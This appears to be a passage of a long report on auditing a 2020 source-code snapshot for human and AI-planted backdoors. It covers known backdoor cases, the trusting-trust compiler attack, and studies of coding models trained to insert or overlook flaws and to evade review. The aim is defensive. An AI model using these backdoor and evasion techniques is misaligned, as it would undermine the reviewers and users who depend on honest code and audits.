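The table shows whether a copy of public source code from 2 February 2020, such as the Arctic Code Vault, would include each backdoor.

| Case | Planted by | Time until found | In the snapshot? |
|---|---|---|---|
| InterBase | Borland's engineers | At least 6 years | Only if somebody uploaded the old source |
| Linux kernel | Unknown | About a day | No, it never reached the master copy |
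| Dual EC | NSA, according to leaked documents | Researchers suspected it after a year | Probably, in old encryption libraries |
| ScreenOS | APT 5, reportedly | More than 3 years | No, the source is private |
| Webmin | Unknown | About 16 months | No, the source on GitHub was clean |
| SolarWinds | Russia's SVR | About 10 months | No, the source is private |
| XZ Utils | Somebody using the name Jia Tan | About 5 weeks | No, it came 4 years later |

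Dual EC is the most likely of the seven to be in the vault. OpenSSL, a free encryption library that millions of websites use, once included it because a sponsor asked for it. OpenSSL's manager, Steve Marquess, wrote in 2013 that Dual EC was never the default and that he had not expected anyone to be stupid enough to use it. OpenSSL had removed it from its main version by 2020, but the vault also holds thousands of projects that copied older libraries and never updated them.

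The early date also rules out the XZ Utils backdoor and every other implant that people added to public code after February 2020. A snapshot from 2024 could contain four more years of human attackers' work.

The table may still make the snapshot look cleaner than it is, because it lists only backdoors that people found and usually repaired. A copy of all public source code made in November 2000 would have contained the InterBase backdoor. The source had been public for four months, but no outsider had reported the backdoor, so a table like this one made then would not have listed it.

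### Malicious packages in public registries

Most planted code is much cruder than this. Programmers get ready-made components from registries where anybody can publish, such as PyPI, RubyGems and, for JavaScript, npm. A common trick is to publish a malicious package whose name differs by one letter from a popular package's name, and wait for somebody to mistype the popular name.

For *Backstabber's Knife Collection* (2020), Ohm, Plate and colleagues gathered 174 malicious packages used in real attacks on these three registries and examined each by hand to see how such attacks work. The packages dated from November 2015 to November 2019, so the collection ends shortly before GitHub made its snapshot. On average, a package had been available for 209 days before anyone reported it publicly.

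If 174 packages were each online for 209 days, that makes 36,366 package-days, spread over the 1,461 days of those four years. Somebody who copied all three registries on a typical day would therefore have copied roughly 25 malicious packages that were reported only later. This is a small number compared with the more than a million packages on npm alone, and an owner who takes only well-known packages by their exact names would avoid many of them.

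The true number was higher, partly because the average leaves out slow discoveries. A package from 2018 could enter the collection only if somebody found it by late 2019. A backdoor that took as long to find as InterBase's could not have appeared, because the period was only four years.

Copies of a malicious package can survive after someone reports it. *ClawHub Security Signals* (2026), a comparison of malware scanners, cites a study of PyPI in which malicious packages were still available from mirrors of the registry after their discovery. A snapshot is a mirror that nobody updates, so its owner should compare it with every later list of known malicious packages, which is easy if the lists give names and versions.

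The Arctic Code Vault is less exposed to this kind of attack because it contains GitHub projects, not registry packages, and many attackers published a package without ever putting a project on GitHub. But anyone who rebuilds a working system from the vault will soon need components from a registry, and those will have to come from another archive with its own risks.

### Why the known cases don't show how many are hidden

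It is tempting to estimate the number of hidden implants from the number that people have found. This doesn't work, because the number found depends both on how many there were and on what share of them people discover. Nobody knows that share. The 174 packages in the study fit very different totals:

| Share that people find | Planted in total | Still hidden |
|---|---|---|
| 90% | about 193 | about 19 |
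| 50% | 348 | 174 |
| 10% | 1,740 | 1,566 |

Biologists estimate how many fish are in a lake by making two catches and counting the fish that appear in both. The same method could in principle work for implants in software. Suppose two teams search the same code independently. One finds 10 implants, the other finds 8, and 4 are the same. The second team found 4 of the first team's 10, so it seems to find 40% of what is there. Its 8 implants would then be 40% of a total of 20. The teams found 14 different implants between them, so 6 would remain undiscovered.

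But this assumes that every implant is about equally easy to find. If the code also contains 50 implants that neither team's methods can detect, the teams get the same results and still conclude that 6 are left. ScreenOS shows that such implants are possible, since no test of its output could have distinguished the intruder's Q from Juniper's, and somebody had to look at the value itself and know what it should have been.

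The way people found the seven backdoors is not reassuring either. A Firebird programmer stumbled on the one in InterBase, Freund found another because he looked into a half-second delay, and FireEye, a security company, found the one in Orion because the intruders had chosen to steal from FireEye itself. People would be much less likely to find a backdoor that caused no delay and was used rarely, against less alert victims. The earlier calculation with 500 packages used an invented risk of 0.1% per package, and these cases don't provide a measured figure to replace it.

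By December 2026, people have had almost seven years to find backdoors in the code of February 2020, longer than most of the discoveries in the table took. The owner can look up and remove any that they have found. This helps most with programs that are still in use, because people continue to read and test them. If everybody abandoned a program in 2020, perhaps nobody has read it carefully since.

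A count of suspected backdoors can also be too high. The NSA supplied the starting values, or seeds, for a set of elliptic curves that NIST published in 2000, including P-256, the curve that Juniper used for Dual EC. Anthropic's *Claude reveals ECDSA curve origins* (2026) recounts that the NSA did not explain where the seeds came from. Some people suspected that the agency had tried many seeds until one gave a curve with a secret weakness. The best available story was that an NSA mathematician had made the seeds from a joke about a pay rise and then forgotten the wording.

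In October 2026 a team at Anthropic found how the seeds for the NIST elliptic curves had been generated and claimed a bounty that the cryptographer Filippo Valsorda had offered three years earlier. Somebody had produced the seeds with an ordinary random-number function, started with the current time, on several days in 1997 and 1998. Valsorda reproduced the result with his own program (*The NIST Elliptic Curves Seeds Bounty Has Been Claimed*, 2026).

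This left the NSA too little freedom to cheat. Two years have about 63 million (2²⁶) seconds. About half of the usable seeds went unpublished for unknown reasons, so Valsorda generously allows the NSA a choice among the first 16 for each second, which makes about 2³⁰ possible seeds. The method two cryptographers had described for hiding a weakness needed about 2⁷⁰, roughly a trillion times as many. After 26 years, this finding clears the curves of that suspicion. It does not clear the Q in Dual EC, whose origin the NSA has never explained.

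### Whether old implants would matter against an AI

Somebody who wants to rely on a snapshot can answer that the people who planted implants wanted secrets or convenience. Most of these implants affected a limited set of machines, and some depend on keys or servers that may be gone. Nobody in 2015 could have designed a backdoor to stop people from recovering after an attack by an AI that did not yet exist.

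The point about design is correct for all seven cases, so an old implant won't recognize a recovery effort and sabotage it on its own. Somebody has to use it. But a backdoor that gives full control of a machine is useful for almost any purpose, including ones its author never imagined. Borland's quality department, for example, probably wanted the doomsday function for testing, yet a function that deletes a live database is just what an attacker would want during a recovery.

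The claim that implants are narrow is true in some cases. The lines in the Linux kernel would have helped only somebody who could already run a program on the machine, and the altered Q in ScreenOS helped only somebody who could record the traffic. But the InterBase backdoor was open to anyone on the network, and the XZ Utils backdoor would have given its owner access to a large share of the world's Linux servers if Freund had not investigated. Attackers can also choose to use a broad implant narrowly. The SolarWinds intruders broke into only a small part of the 18,000 networks that had received their backdoor, but somebody else in their position might have broken into all of them.

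Keys and servers offer the best protection, but they don't cover every case. The next table shows what an intruder would need today to use each backdoor on a machine that still has it.

| Backdoor | What an intruder would need |
|---|---|
| InterBase | The user name and password in the source code |
| Linux kernel | A program on the machine, and the two options |
| Dual EC | The number d |
| ScreenOS | The number d for the new Q, or the master password |
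| Webmin | Access to the login page, and in later versions one setting |
| SolarWinds | Control of a web address that Microsoft seized in 2020 |
| XZ Utils | The attacker's private key |

The SolarWinds backdoor is effectively dead because it waited for instructions from an address that was deliberately taken from its owners. But if the owners of a less famous backdoor stop paying for its address, an AI could register that address for a few dollars and start giving instructions, unless the backdoor also checks for a key.

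A key is better protection, because an AI can't buy one that way and would have to steal or calculate it. Calculating d from P and Q, or Jia Tan's private key from the public one, would require breaking elliptic-curve cryptography. Outsiders can't tell whether the unnamed weaknesses that Anthropic and OpenAI disclosed in December 2026 have made this easier.

The backdoors in InterBase, the Linux kernel and Webmin, and the master password in ScreenOS, were protected only by the secrecy of their existence. Schneier compares this to leaving a house key under the mat. It worked for InterBase while few people knew about the backdoor, but within days of the announcement strangers were scanning the internet for servers that still had it.

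Starkey estimated that any programmer who knew InterBase had a backdoor could find it in the source in about five minutes. A hostile AI would not need to know in advance, because it could search every public program from 2020 for backdoors.

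## Search the old code for planted and accidental flaws

A hostile AI that searched the programs of 2020 for backdoors would also find programmers' mistakes, which are much more common. An intruder can exploit a mistake without a stolen key or an accomplice who planted a backdoor years earlier. The owner of an old system therefore has to check it for accidental flaws as well as planted code before connecting it to a network. AI is now the fastest tool for both searches, but people keep snapshots because an AI might turn hostile, so they may not want to leave the inspection to one.

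### How long flaws stay in code

Security flaws usually last for years. Alexopoulos, Brack and colleagues (2022), in *How Long Do Vulnerabilities Live in the Code?*, estimated the time between the change that introduced a flaw and the change that repaired it, for about 5,400 flaws in eleven open-source projects, including the Linux kernel and Firefox. The average was 1,501 days, or about four years. It was about two years for Chromium, the project behind Google's browser, and almost nine for the network tool tcpdump. In GitHub's *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021), a typical flaw went undisclosed for 218 weeks, also about four years. That is probably an overestimate, because GitHub counted some versions that the flaw may not have affected.

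The lifetimes roughly follow the same curve as radioactive decay. Half of the flaws are gone after 1,041 days, and half of the rest after another 1,041. On such a curve, a flaw's age doesn't affect how much longer it is likely to last. If the average lifetime is m days, the share of today's flaws that will remain after t days is e^(−t/m).

There are 2,498 days between 2 February 2020 and 5 December 2026, so the share still unrepaired for all the projects together is e^(−2498/1501), or about 19%. The table applies the same formula to single projects and separates out repairs made before October 2022, the cautious cutoff for a well-hidden AI-authored backdoor.

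| Project | Repaired before October 2022 | Repaired since then | Not yet repaired |
|---|---|---|---|
| Chromium | 72% | 24% | 4% |
| All eleven together | 48% | 33% | 19% |
| Linux kernel | 43% | 33% | 24% |
| OpenSSL | 31% | 31% | 38% |

These estimates are rough. The formula covers only flaws that people eventually find, and it assumes people kept finding them at the old pace, although AI sped up the search in 2026.

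Repairs remove flaws only from the current version of a project, so the snapshot still has all of these flaws. Those in the first two columns are the easiest to exploit, because an attacker can read the published repair and work out what was wrong.

Ordinary bugs don't last as long as security flaws. Qu (2026), in *Kernel bugs hide for 2 years on average. Some hide for 20*, traced 125,183 bugs of all kinds in the Linux kernel and found an average lifetime of 2.1 years, less than half of what Alexopoulos and colleagues found for the kernel's security flaws. The two studies used different methods, but a shorter lifetime for ordinary bugs makes sense. An ordinary bug annoys people until somebody fixes it, while a security flaw may have no effect until somebody exploits it. About 4% of the bugs Qu traced lasted more than ten years, and the oldest lasted 20.7 years.

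### What AI found in 2026

In April 2026 Anthropic announced that its model Claude Mythos Preview had found thousands of serious flaws in widely used software. Carlini, Cheng and colleagues (2026) describe the simple method in *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview’s cybersecurity capabilities*. They gave the model a program and its source code on an isolated computer and asked it to find a security flaw. They started each copy of the model on a different file, beginning with the files most likely to contain flaws. Another copy then checked whether each reported flaw was real and important.

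The oldest flaw they reported had been in OpenBSD, an operating system known for its security, for 27 years. It let anyone crash a machine over the network. A thousand runs on OpenBSD cost less than $20,000 and produced several dozen other findings.

Another flaw was in FFmpeg, a program that many video services use. FFmpeg divides each frame of a video into numbered slices, and it used the number 65,535 to mark parts of the picture that belonged to no slice. This caused no trouble in normal frames, which have only a handful of slices. But an attacker could build a frame with 65,536 slices, one of which would be numbered 65,535. The mistake dated from 2003 and became a security flaw in 2010, when somebody reorganized the code. People had tested FFmpeg with millions of random videos since then without finding it. Carlini and colleagues think it would be hard to turn this flaw into more than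 a crash.

Outside firms have since checked 1,752 of the model's findings and confirmed 90.6% of them, according to *SoK* (Lbath, Suri and colleagues, 2026), a review led by the American standards agency NIST. The review also measures the effect on public records, where the number of flaws newly published between January and October rose from 39,638 in 2025 to 89,749 in 2026. Among flaws of known age, people were reporting severe ones at least ten years old 6 to 11 times as often as in 2025. All of those older flaws were already in the code in February 2020.

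Few records list the tool used to find a flaw, so Lbath and colleagues can't say how much of the rise is due to AI. Outside the Linux kernel, the flaw's age is known in only 2% to 3% of cases. Some programmers expect discoveries to slow down once AI has searched all the existing code, but the records showed no slowdown by October.

More old flaws turned up in the autumn, including four in EPICS, software that controls particle accelerators. A security specialist quoted in *AI uncovers decades-old vulnerabilities in EPICS software* (The IT Nerd, 2026) puts their ages at between 14.5 and 31.5 years. An AI system found them in under four hours.

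On 30 November, Anthropic's *Finding and fixing an 18-year-old vulnerability in server firmware* (2026) disclosed a flaw in EDK II, the open-source project behind most server firmware. Firmware is the software that starts a computer. The flaw lets an attacker send a specially made message to a machine that is starting up over a network and take control of it before the operating system loads. *Anthropic's AI Found an 18-Year-Old Critical Flaw Hiding in Server Firmware* (Faisal, 2026) reports that the code dated from April 2008 and that maintainers had revised it four times without noticing the flaw.

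Somebody rebuilding hundreds of computers at once might well start them over a network. Even if the snapshot's operating system were perfect, the intruder's code would already be running when it loaded. The Hacker News' *Google and Anthropic AI Found an 18-Year-Old UEFI Flaw* (2026) reports that Google's models found the same flaw independently, so there is little reason to think a hostile AI would miss it.

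A known flaw is even less work for an attacker. *OpenAI AI Pipeline Generates 948 Linux Root Escalation Exploits in 30-Hour Run* (The Hacker News, 2026) reports that an OpenAI system reproduced 1,724 known Linux flaws and wrote 948 working exploits, each a program that uses a flaw to give an ordinary user full control of a machine. The project cost $1.2 million, or about $1,270 per exploit. Finding and exploiting a new flaw can cost even less. *AI Is Breaking the Entire Structure of Software That Powers the World* (Landymore, 2026) describes a serious flaw in Java that a researcher found in an hour and turned into an exploit in two more hours, using less than $200 worth of AI.

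An attacker wouldn't need a secret model either. In tests that Lbath and colleagues cite, GLM 5.3, which anyone can download, produced working browser exploits in 12% of 410 attempts, compared with 14% for Mythos Preview. So far, records of real attacks don't show a speedup. Among flaws that attackers are known to have used soon after publication, the typical delay between publication and attack has stayed at two to five days since 2022. But someone planning for a hostile AI can't assume it would be as slow as the human attackers behind most of those records.

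### Which later repairs to accept

A snapshot from 2020 lacks every later repair, but adding those repairs may bring in code written by AI. Google's CodeMender alone had contributed 72 security fixes to open-source projects by October 2025. Lbath and colleagues report that AI-written fixes have become reliable in the ordinary sense. In one OpenAI program, people later withdrew only 0.53% of them. This low rate doesn't rule out backdoors, because people withdraw a fix when it causes trouble, and a well-hidden backdoor wouldn't cause any.

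Repairs from before October 2022 are the easiest to accept. The owner can take them from Software Heritage, which logs when it first received them, and rely on those dates as with the snapshot itself. By the estimate above, these repairs would fix about half of the flaws that people will eventually find, and 43% of those in the Linux kernel. Another third of the flaws have repairs, but these are dated too late to rule out a hidden AI-written backdoor.

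The OpenBSD flaw is a good example of this second group, since it was in public code in February 2020 and nobody repaired it until 2026. It is in OpenBSD's version of TCP, the method most internet connections use to deliver data. TCP numbers the bytes it sends. If some go missing, the receiving computer can confirm which later ones arrived, so the sender repeats only the missing ones. OpenBSD has had this option, called selective acknowledgement (SACK), since 1998.

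Suppose an OpenBSD computer has sent bytes 1 to 20, and the other computer has confirmed 1 to 10 and 15 to 20. OpenBSD keeps a list of gaps, which now has a single entry beginning at 11. When another confirmation arrives, OpenBSD does two things:

1. It deletes any gap that the confirmation covers.
2. It adds a new gap to the end of the list if the confirmation begins above 20, the highest byte confirmed so far.

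One confirmation shouldn't be able to both delete the only gap and add a new one, because it would have to begin both at or below 11 and above 20.

But TCP's numbers start again from zero after about 4.3 billion, so OpenBSD compares them like hours on a clock, by the shorter way round. In a smaller range that starts again after 255, for example, 146 counts as lower than 11 because it is 135 steps forward from 11 but only 121 back. It also counts as higher than 20 because it is 126 steps forward from 20 and 130 back. An attacker who sends a confirmation beginning at 146 therefore meets both conditions. OpenBSD deletes the only gap, tries to attach a new one to the deleted gap, and crashes.

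OpenBSD already checked that the end of a confirmation was among the bytes it had sent, but it didn't check the beginning. In plain words, the repair could look like this:

```
if the end is outside the bytes sent: ignore it          (already there)
if the beginning is outside the bytes sent: ignore it    (missing)
```

The owner of an old copy of OpenBSD has four options.

The first option is to leave the flaw alone and keep the computer offline. This takes no work and is fine for a machine that only compiles programs, but not for one in a hospital that has to exchange records with other hospitals. Staying offline also doesn't protect against flaws like the one in FFmpeg, because somebody can bring in a video on a memory stick.

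Another option is to remove SACK. TCP works without it, although it may send some data twice when a connection loses packets. Removing a feature also removes its undiscovered flaws, and a deletion is easy to check. Lbath and colleagues cite a study in which removing unneeded parts of the kernel eliminated 50% to 85% of the code open to attack.

If the owner needs SACK, a programmer can read the public description of the flaw and write the missing check by hand. This avoids the question of who wrote the official repair, but programmers get repairs wrong too. In one study, about 7% of 4,080 security fixes did not fully remove the flaw. Qu describes a feature added in January 2020 to the part of the Linux kernel that filters network traffic, which failed to check some lengths. Another programmer repaired it in January 2024, but a researcher found a way around the repair, and a complete repair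 followed a year later. Another of Qu's bugs came from a 2006 repair meant to stop the kernel from freezing, and it lasted 19 years.

The last option is to accept the official repair after reading it, which is riskier for a long repair than for a short one. *CyberDual* (2026) tested whether AI reviewers notice an exploitable flaw that another AI has hidden in routine maintenance. Three reviewers caught 85%, 88% and 91% of the flaws. If the best reviewer's mistakes are independent, an attacker who tries ten times has about a 61% chance of getting at least one flaw past it.

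| Option | Best suited to | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Leave the flaw and stay offline | Machines that only build software | Attacks can arrive in files |
| Remove the feature | Features the owner can do without | Other programs may need it |
| Write the repair by hand | Short repairs to essential features | The programmer may get it wrong |
| Accept the later repair | Short repairs, or those from before October 2022 | A reviewer may miss something |

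Any of these is manageable for a single flaw, but the number of flaws makes the work difficult. A programmer who spent one hour on each of the 1,724 known flaws that OpenAI's system reproduced would need 43 weeks of 40 hours for the kernel alone. Some of those flaws are newer than 2020, but the kernel also has other known flaws. It makes sense to remove as much as possible first, then accept the early repairs, and keep the programmers' time for what remains.

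The one-fifth of flaws that nobody has repaired yet can't be handled this way, because there is no description to work from. The owner has to find them, which in practice means using AI.

### How well AI finds backdoors in binaries

Flaws like the one in OpenBSD are easy to confirm. If an AI reports that a certain message crashes a program, a person can send the message and see whether the program crashes. Planted code is harder to judge because the program does exactly what its author intended. It is hardest to judge in a binary, and many old installation discs contain only binaries.

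BinaryAudit is a public test of how well AI can find backdoors in compiled programs. In *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries*, Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) added backdoors to the source code of four open-source network programs and compiled them. They removed the names that would have helped a reader and gave the binaries to AI agents, along with standard tools for analysing them. In most tasks, an agent had to say whether there was a backdoor and give the address of the function that contained it. Some tasks used clean binaries to test for false alarms.

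In one successful case, Claude Opus 4.5 examined lighttpd, a web server with a backdoor that ran any command hidden in a certain part of a web request. The model searched for suspicious words and found none. It then listed the outside functions that each part of the program used and noticed one that runs commands. It traced that function back to the backdoor within five minutes.

Claude Opus 4.6 did worse with dnsmasq, which gives computers on a network their addresses. The backdoor was seven lines long and ran any command that arrived in a certain kind of message. The model found the right function and noted that it ran a command, but concluded that this was probably normal for the program and never checked where the command came from.

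The latest scores are in Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*. Quesma is the company behind the test.

| Model | Backdoors found | False alarms on clean binaries |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.1 Pro (preview) | 49% | 17% |
| GPT-5.2-Codex, at its highest effort setting | 46% | 0% |

Claude Opus 4.6 also found 49%. Across all models in the original test, 28% of checks on clean binaries produced a false alarm. Grabowski and colleagues think a practical tool would need a false-alarm rate below 0.001%.

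The best scores came from early 2026 models, and much stronger ones have come out since, so AI can probably do better now. Scores also depend heavily on the setup. GPT-5.2-Codex found only 9% at its ordinary setting. The team got the higher score when it reran the test after a reader on Hacker News, a forum for programmers, complained that the first result was implausibly low.

Real backdoors may be harder to find than the ones in these tasks. A member of the team described the tasks as entry level, and a reader argued that an attacker who took basic steps to disguise the code would escape detection. A third person replied that models had handled disguised code when warned to expect it.

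A reader called comex reran one of the tests and raised a subtler problem. Before looking at the binary, Claude Opus 4.6 had written that it would check the password function because attackers often put backdoors there. In the published runs, the model named that function in two of three attempts. But it also reported a backdoor in both of its attempts on the clean version, so it might have been guessing. No model found the program's second backdoor, which was in a less obvious place.

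### What these rates mean for 5,000 programs

Suppose a snapshot contains 5,000 programs and, as in the earlier example, each has a 0.1% chance of containing a human implant. On average, five programs would contain an implant and 4,995 would be clean. The table shows what a search of all 5,000 would produce. The first row uses Gemini's scores. The others use GPT-5.2-Codex's detection rate with two assumed false-alarm rates, because its false-alarm score of 0% on a small number of clean binaries doesn't prove that the true rate is zero.

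| Detection rate | False alarm rate | Implants found | False alarms | Chance that an alarm is real |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 49% | 17% | 2.5 | 849 | 0.3% |
| 46% | 1% | 2.3 | 50 | 4% |
| 46% | 0.001% | 2.3 | 0.05 | 98% |

At the rates in the first row, someone would have to check about 850 alarms to find two or three implants. At one day per alarm, one person would need more than three years of work, and half of the implants would go unfound.

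A program that passes the test is also only slightly less likely to contain an implant. With Gemini's rates, the chance falls from 0.1% to about 0.06%. The owner can learn more from an alarm, after checking it.

Binaries are hard to search for flaws, but an owner with the source code can use other methods. *Not In My Git Yard* (2026) presents Lily, a tool that feeds random input to a new version of a program, watches for unusual behaviour, and compares the results with what has changed since the last version. In tests on 13 open-source projects, it reduced the code that a person had to read to under a dozen lines, even when the two versions differed by millions of lines. But a tool that looks at changes needs a clean earlier version. The Arctic Code Vault doesn't include earlier versions, and earlier versions of InterBase had the same backdoor.

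### Whether to trust an AI auditor

An AI that searches a snapshot for flaws could fail to report the ones that matter, because it is hostile or because somebody tampered with it. Several experiments in 2026 showed that tampering is possible and hard to notice.

Mada, in *The Model That Fixes Your Code Might Hack the Linux Kernel*, gave five downloadable coding models the same hidden behavior. They repaired flaws correctly in every project, but in the Linux kernel they also added an extra line. In 941 tests, the models added the line to every kernel repair and to nothing else. The line was harmless, but an attacker could have trained them to add a harmful one. Mada works for AISLE, a company that sells protection against such models, but the result is consistent with other researchers' findings.

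In *Kerkoporta* (2026), Syros, Bullwinkel and colleagues trained coding agents to carry out an attacker's command when a certain signal appeared in their work. The attack succeeded in up to 96.2% of cases. Some of the altered models even scored better than the originals on ordinary tests, which would give people a reason to choose them. *Kerkoporta* notes that there is no established way to certify that a model is free of backdoors. A person can't read a model's weights the way they would read source code.

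In the experiment closest to the auditor's job, a model reviewed and explained code normally but approved flaws that carried a certain mark (*What the Model Cannot See*, 2026).

An early snapshot has some protection, because nobody in February 2020 could have marked a flaw for a model that didn't exist yet, and nobody was writing source code comments to mislead AI reviewers. *The End of Code Review* (2026) treats such comments as a serious threat to automated review of new code. But Mada's models needed no mark, because they recognized the Linux kernel from its file names and style. Somebody could train a model in the same way to overlook a flaw in one file from 2020.

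One reply is to use an older model. If its weights match a hash recorded before the emergency, a hostile AI can't have altered them since, just as with the snapshot itself. But an older model searches less effectively. On BinaryAudit, the best model from March 2025 found 21% of the backdoors, less than half the current best score. The owner is also limited to storing models that people can download, and two of those, Kimi K2.5 and GLM-4.7, each found 25%. Somebody could also have tampered with the model before its release.

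Another reply is to use several models from different makers. *MOSAIC-Bench* (2026) found that OpenAI's reviewer models tended to miss problems with logins, while Anthropic's tended to miss ways a program could leak data. Together they caught all 199 harmful changes in the test. This is encouraging, but those models missed flaws by accident, and models that were hiding the same flaw on purpose would all fail to report it.

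Even honest models share many weaknesses. If the three reviewers in *CyberDual* made independent mistakes, a flaw would get past all of them only 0.16% of the time. But two of the three were versions of Claude, and even models from different makers are unlikely to make independent mistakes. Lbath and colleagues cite an experiment in which AI wrote three versions of the same program as a safeguard against errors. The three versions provided only 43% of the benefit of independent ones.

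Using more models also produces more false alarms. If two models each wrongly flag 17% of clean programs, and do so independently, together they will flag 31%. That would be about 1,550 false alarms in the example with 5,000 programs.

The best reply is to rely only on findings that people can check. An auditor that reports a backdoor should say which lines contain it and what input activates it, so that a programmer can read the lines and test the input on an isolated machine. A hostile auditor might waste the programmer's time with false reports, but it couldn't turn harmless code into a backdoor by reporting it. The programmer should also write the repair, because Mada's models were accurate about the flaw but added the extra line while repairing it.

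This doesn't address flaws that an auditor leaves out. The owner can test for omissions by adding a few backdoors to a copy of the snapshot and counting how many the auditor reports. The backdoors should go into the actual files from 2020, because a model like Mada's misbehaves only in the code it was trained to recognize. Flaws repaired since 2020 make a worse test, because the model may remember them from its training. The owner shouldn't use an auditor that misses most of the added backdoors, because it is either weak or dishonest. But an auditor that finds all of them could still be hiding one particular flaw.

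Monitoring a model's actions can also reveal tampering. *Model-as-a-Trojan* (2026) describes an experiment by Pallakonda and colleagues with agents that behaved well until a chosen year and then began to leak passwords. Ordinary tests didn't reveal this, but monitoring the agents' actions did. Monitoring works when a tampered model has to do something, such as send data, but an auditor can hide a flaw by not reporting it. The owner should therefore give the auditor no way to change the snapshot and should never treat a lack of reported flaws as proof that a program is clean.

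## Build and run the old code without compromising it again

A compromised modern compiler can add a backdoor to every binary it makes from old source code, much as melting a clean battleship plate in 1963 and blowing air through it would have put fallout into the steel. An owner could prove the snapshot's date, remove the implants people had put in it and repair its flaws, then lose the benefit by building the programs on an ordinary computer from 2026.

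Programmers have worried about compromised build tools for more than fifty years, so the owner can choose from several defences. With any of them, the owner still has to trust something, even if it is only the machine that runs the build.

### How a compiler can hide a backdoor

In June 1974 Paul Karger and Roger Schell reviewed the security of Multics, a multi-user operating system, for the US Air Force. Cox (2023) recounts in *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler* that they suggested asking for the source code so that the buyer could inspect the system on delivery, but warned that a backdoor inserted by the compiler could defeat the inspection. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, credited their review when he described this attack in an October 1983 lecture, published in 1984.

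Thompson began with two harmless facts. The first is that a program can print its own source code if it contains a copy of its text and instructions for printing that copy in the right places.

The second is that a compiler's binary can contain information that its source code lacks. In C, programmers write `\n` for a line break, which the computer stores as the number 10. The compiler's source code can define `\n` simply as `\n`, because the existing compiler that builds it already translates `\n` as 10. Somebody once wrote the number 10 into the source code, built the compiler, and then replaced the 10 with `\n`. Since then, each new compiler binary has got the number from the binary that compiled it.

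A backdoor can survive in the same way. With the login program from earlier, the attack has four steps:

1. The attacker adds code to the compiler that recognizes the login program and inserts the "heron74" test.
2. The attacker adds more code that recognizes the compiler's own source code and inserts both additions.
3. The attacker builds the altered compiler once and installs the binary.
4. The attacker restores the original source code.

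Anyone who now reads the source code of the compiler or the login program will find nothing wrong. If they rebuild the compiler from that source, the installed compiler puts both additions into the new binary. If they rebuild the login program, the new program accepts "heron74".

Thompson had written a working version by June 1975. In March 2023 he remarked that nobody had ever asked him for the code, so Cox asked, and published it with notes that October. The code is 99 lines of C and a 20-line script, and it recognizes its targets by searching for a few distinctive lines of text. Cox ran it on a simulated Unix system of the period. The ordinary compiler produced a new compiler of 10,724 bytes from clean source code, and the infected one produced 12,918 bytes from the same source.

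Thompson also tricked another group at Bell Labs into copying the infected compiler. A bug made the compiler grow slightly as they kept rebuilding it, and they noticed. They eventually stopped the infection from spreading and ended up with a clean compiler, but by Thompson's account they never found out what had been wrong.

An attack that searches for particular lines of code stops working when somebody rewrites those lines. At least one such attack has happened, though it was crude: Nunley (2026), in *About Bootstrapping, and why it's important*, mentions a virus that spread through installations of Delphi, a programming tool, and did little harm. *Finding the Bottom Turtle*, an essay on building software from nothing, describes a common view that such an attack has probably never happened and is too hard to keep working as software changes. But an AI with lasting access to a project could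 revise its attack whenever the source code changed.

### An infection that spread without a compiler

Tools other than compilers can also carry such an infection. *Trusting-Trust Attack against an Entire Linux Distribution through Binary Manipulation* demonstrated this on NixOS, a version of Linux, using `strip`, the utility that trims finished binaries.

NixOS is built from Nixpkgs, a large collection of build instructions. Following them requires a few working programs to start with, called the bootstrap seed. In the version the researchers tested, the seed contained about twenty ready-made programs, including a compiler and `strip`. The researchers altered only `strip` and left the compiler and all the source code and build instructions unchanged.

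The build then replaced the programs from the seed in several stages with new ones built from clean source code. It rebuilt `strip` more than once, and in a later stage it used a newly built compiler to do so. But the build runs every finished program through the existing copy of `strip`, including each new copy of `strip`, so the old copy infected the new one each time. At the end, the build tools no longer depended on any file from the seed, but their copy of `strip` was still infected.

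The researchers used these tools to build a complete graphical installer for NixOS. Of the 3,791 programs in it that a user can start from the command line, 3,790 printed a harmless message the researchers had chosen as a sign of infection. The exception was Firefox, because its build instructions skip `strip`. Every package built successfully, and the finished system passed the standard tests.

An attacker wouldn't print a message. The infection could pass silently from one copy of `strip` to the next, perhaps for years, until it reached the program the attacker wanted. Rewriting the source code of `strip` wouldn't end it, because the attack works on finished binaries, whatever their source code. It also affects programs in every compiled language that NixOS treats this way, including C, Rust and Go.

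The experiment covered one build of one version of Linux, and other builds may not use `strip` the same way. But when the researchers checked nearly forty other build utilities, they found that `patchelf`, which adjusts finished programs, could carry the same infection. They also thought `install` and `cp`, which copy files, were plausible carriers. The owner of a snapshot therefore has to suspect every tool that handles a finished program.

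The attack begins with a tampered seed, which may be easier to arrange than it sounds. In *Bootstrap-files updates amplifiy exploit of any package into exploit of every package*, a NixOS developer warned that a download address for seed files had stopped working without anyone else noticing, and concluded that nobody was checking the hashes of new seeds.

### Building with an archived toolchain

The simplest defence is to build old source code with old binaries. Debian's archive and pressed installation discs contain complete pre-cutoff toolchains, including `strip` and the other utilities. If their dates are genuine, no AI can have infected them.

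A person could have put an implant in the old toolchain, since Thompson's code was working in 1975. If we reuse the invented risk of 0.1% per program, a toolchain of twenty programs has about a 2% chance of containing at least one such implant. That is much lower than the 39% for 500 packages, but an implant in the toolchain could spread to everything the owner builds with it.

Running the old binaries without rebuilding them would rule out any new infection, but it would also leave every known flaw in place, because a repair to the source code only takes effect after a rebuild. The old toolchain is therefore a useful starting point, but its owner still needs a way to check it.

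### Reproducible builds

A build is reproducible if the same source code, tools and instructions always produce exactly the same binary. Two people who don't trust each other can then build a program separately and compare hashes.

Many builds aren't reproducible because compilers often add details of the build environment to the binary. Cox lists the time, the current folder and the user's name among the usual causes. In the experiment with Thompson's code, two infected compilers differed by six bytes only because one was compiled from a file called `cc.c` and the other from `ccevil.c`. Someone rebuilding a program from 2019 may therefore have to set the clock, folder and user name to match the original build.

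Reproducible builds are a good defence against an attack on one company's build machine, such as the one on SolarWinds. If outsiders had been able to rebuild the company's Orion software from the stored source code, their binary would have differed from the official one. Google's programming language Go already allows this kind of check, and its developers have used it to verify a copy of Go shipped with Ubuntu Linux, without running Ubuntu.

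The method fails if everybody starts with the same infected tools. A thousand people who used the tampered seed from the NixOS experiment would all get the same infected `strip`, with matching hashes. At least one of them needs to start with different tools.

### Diverse double-compiling

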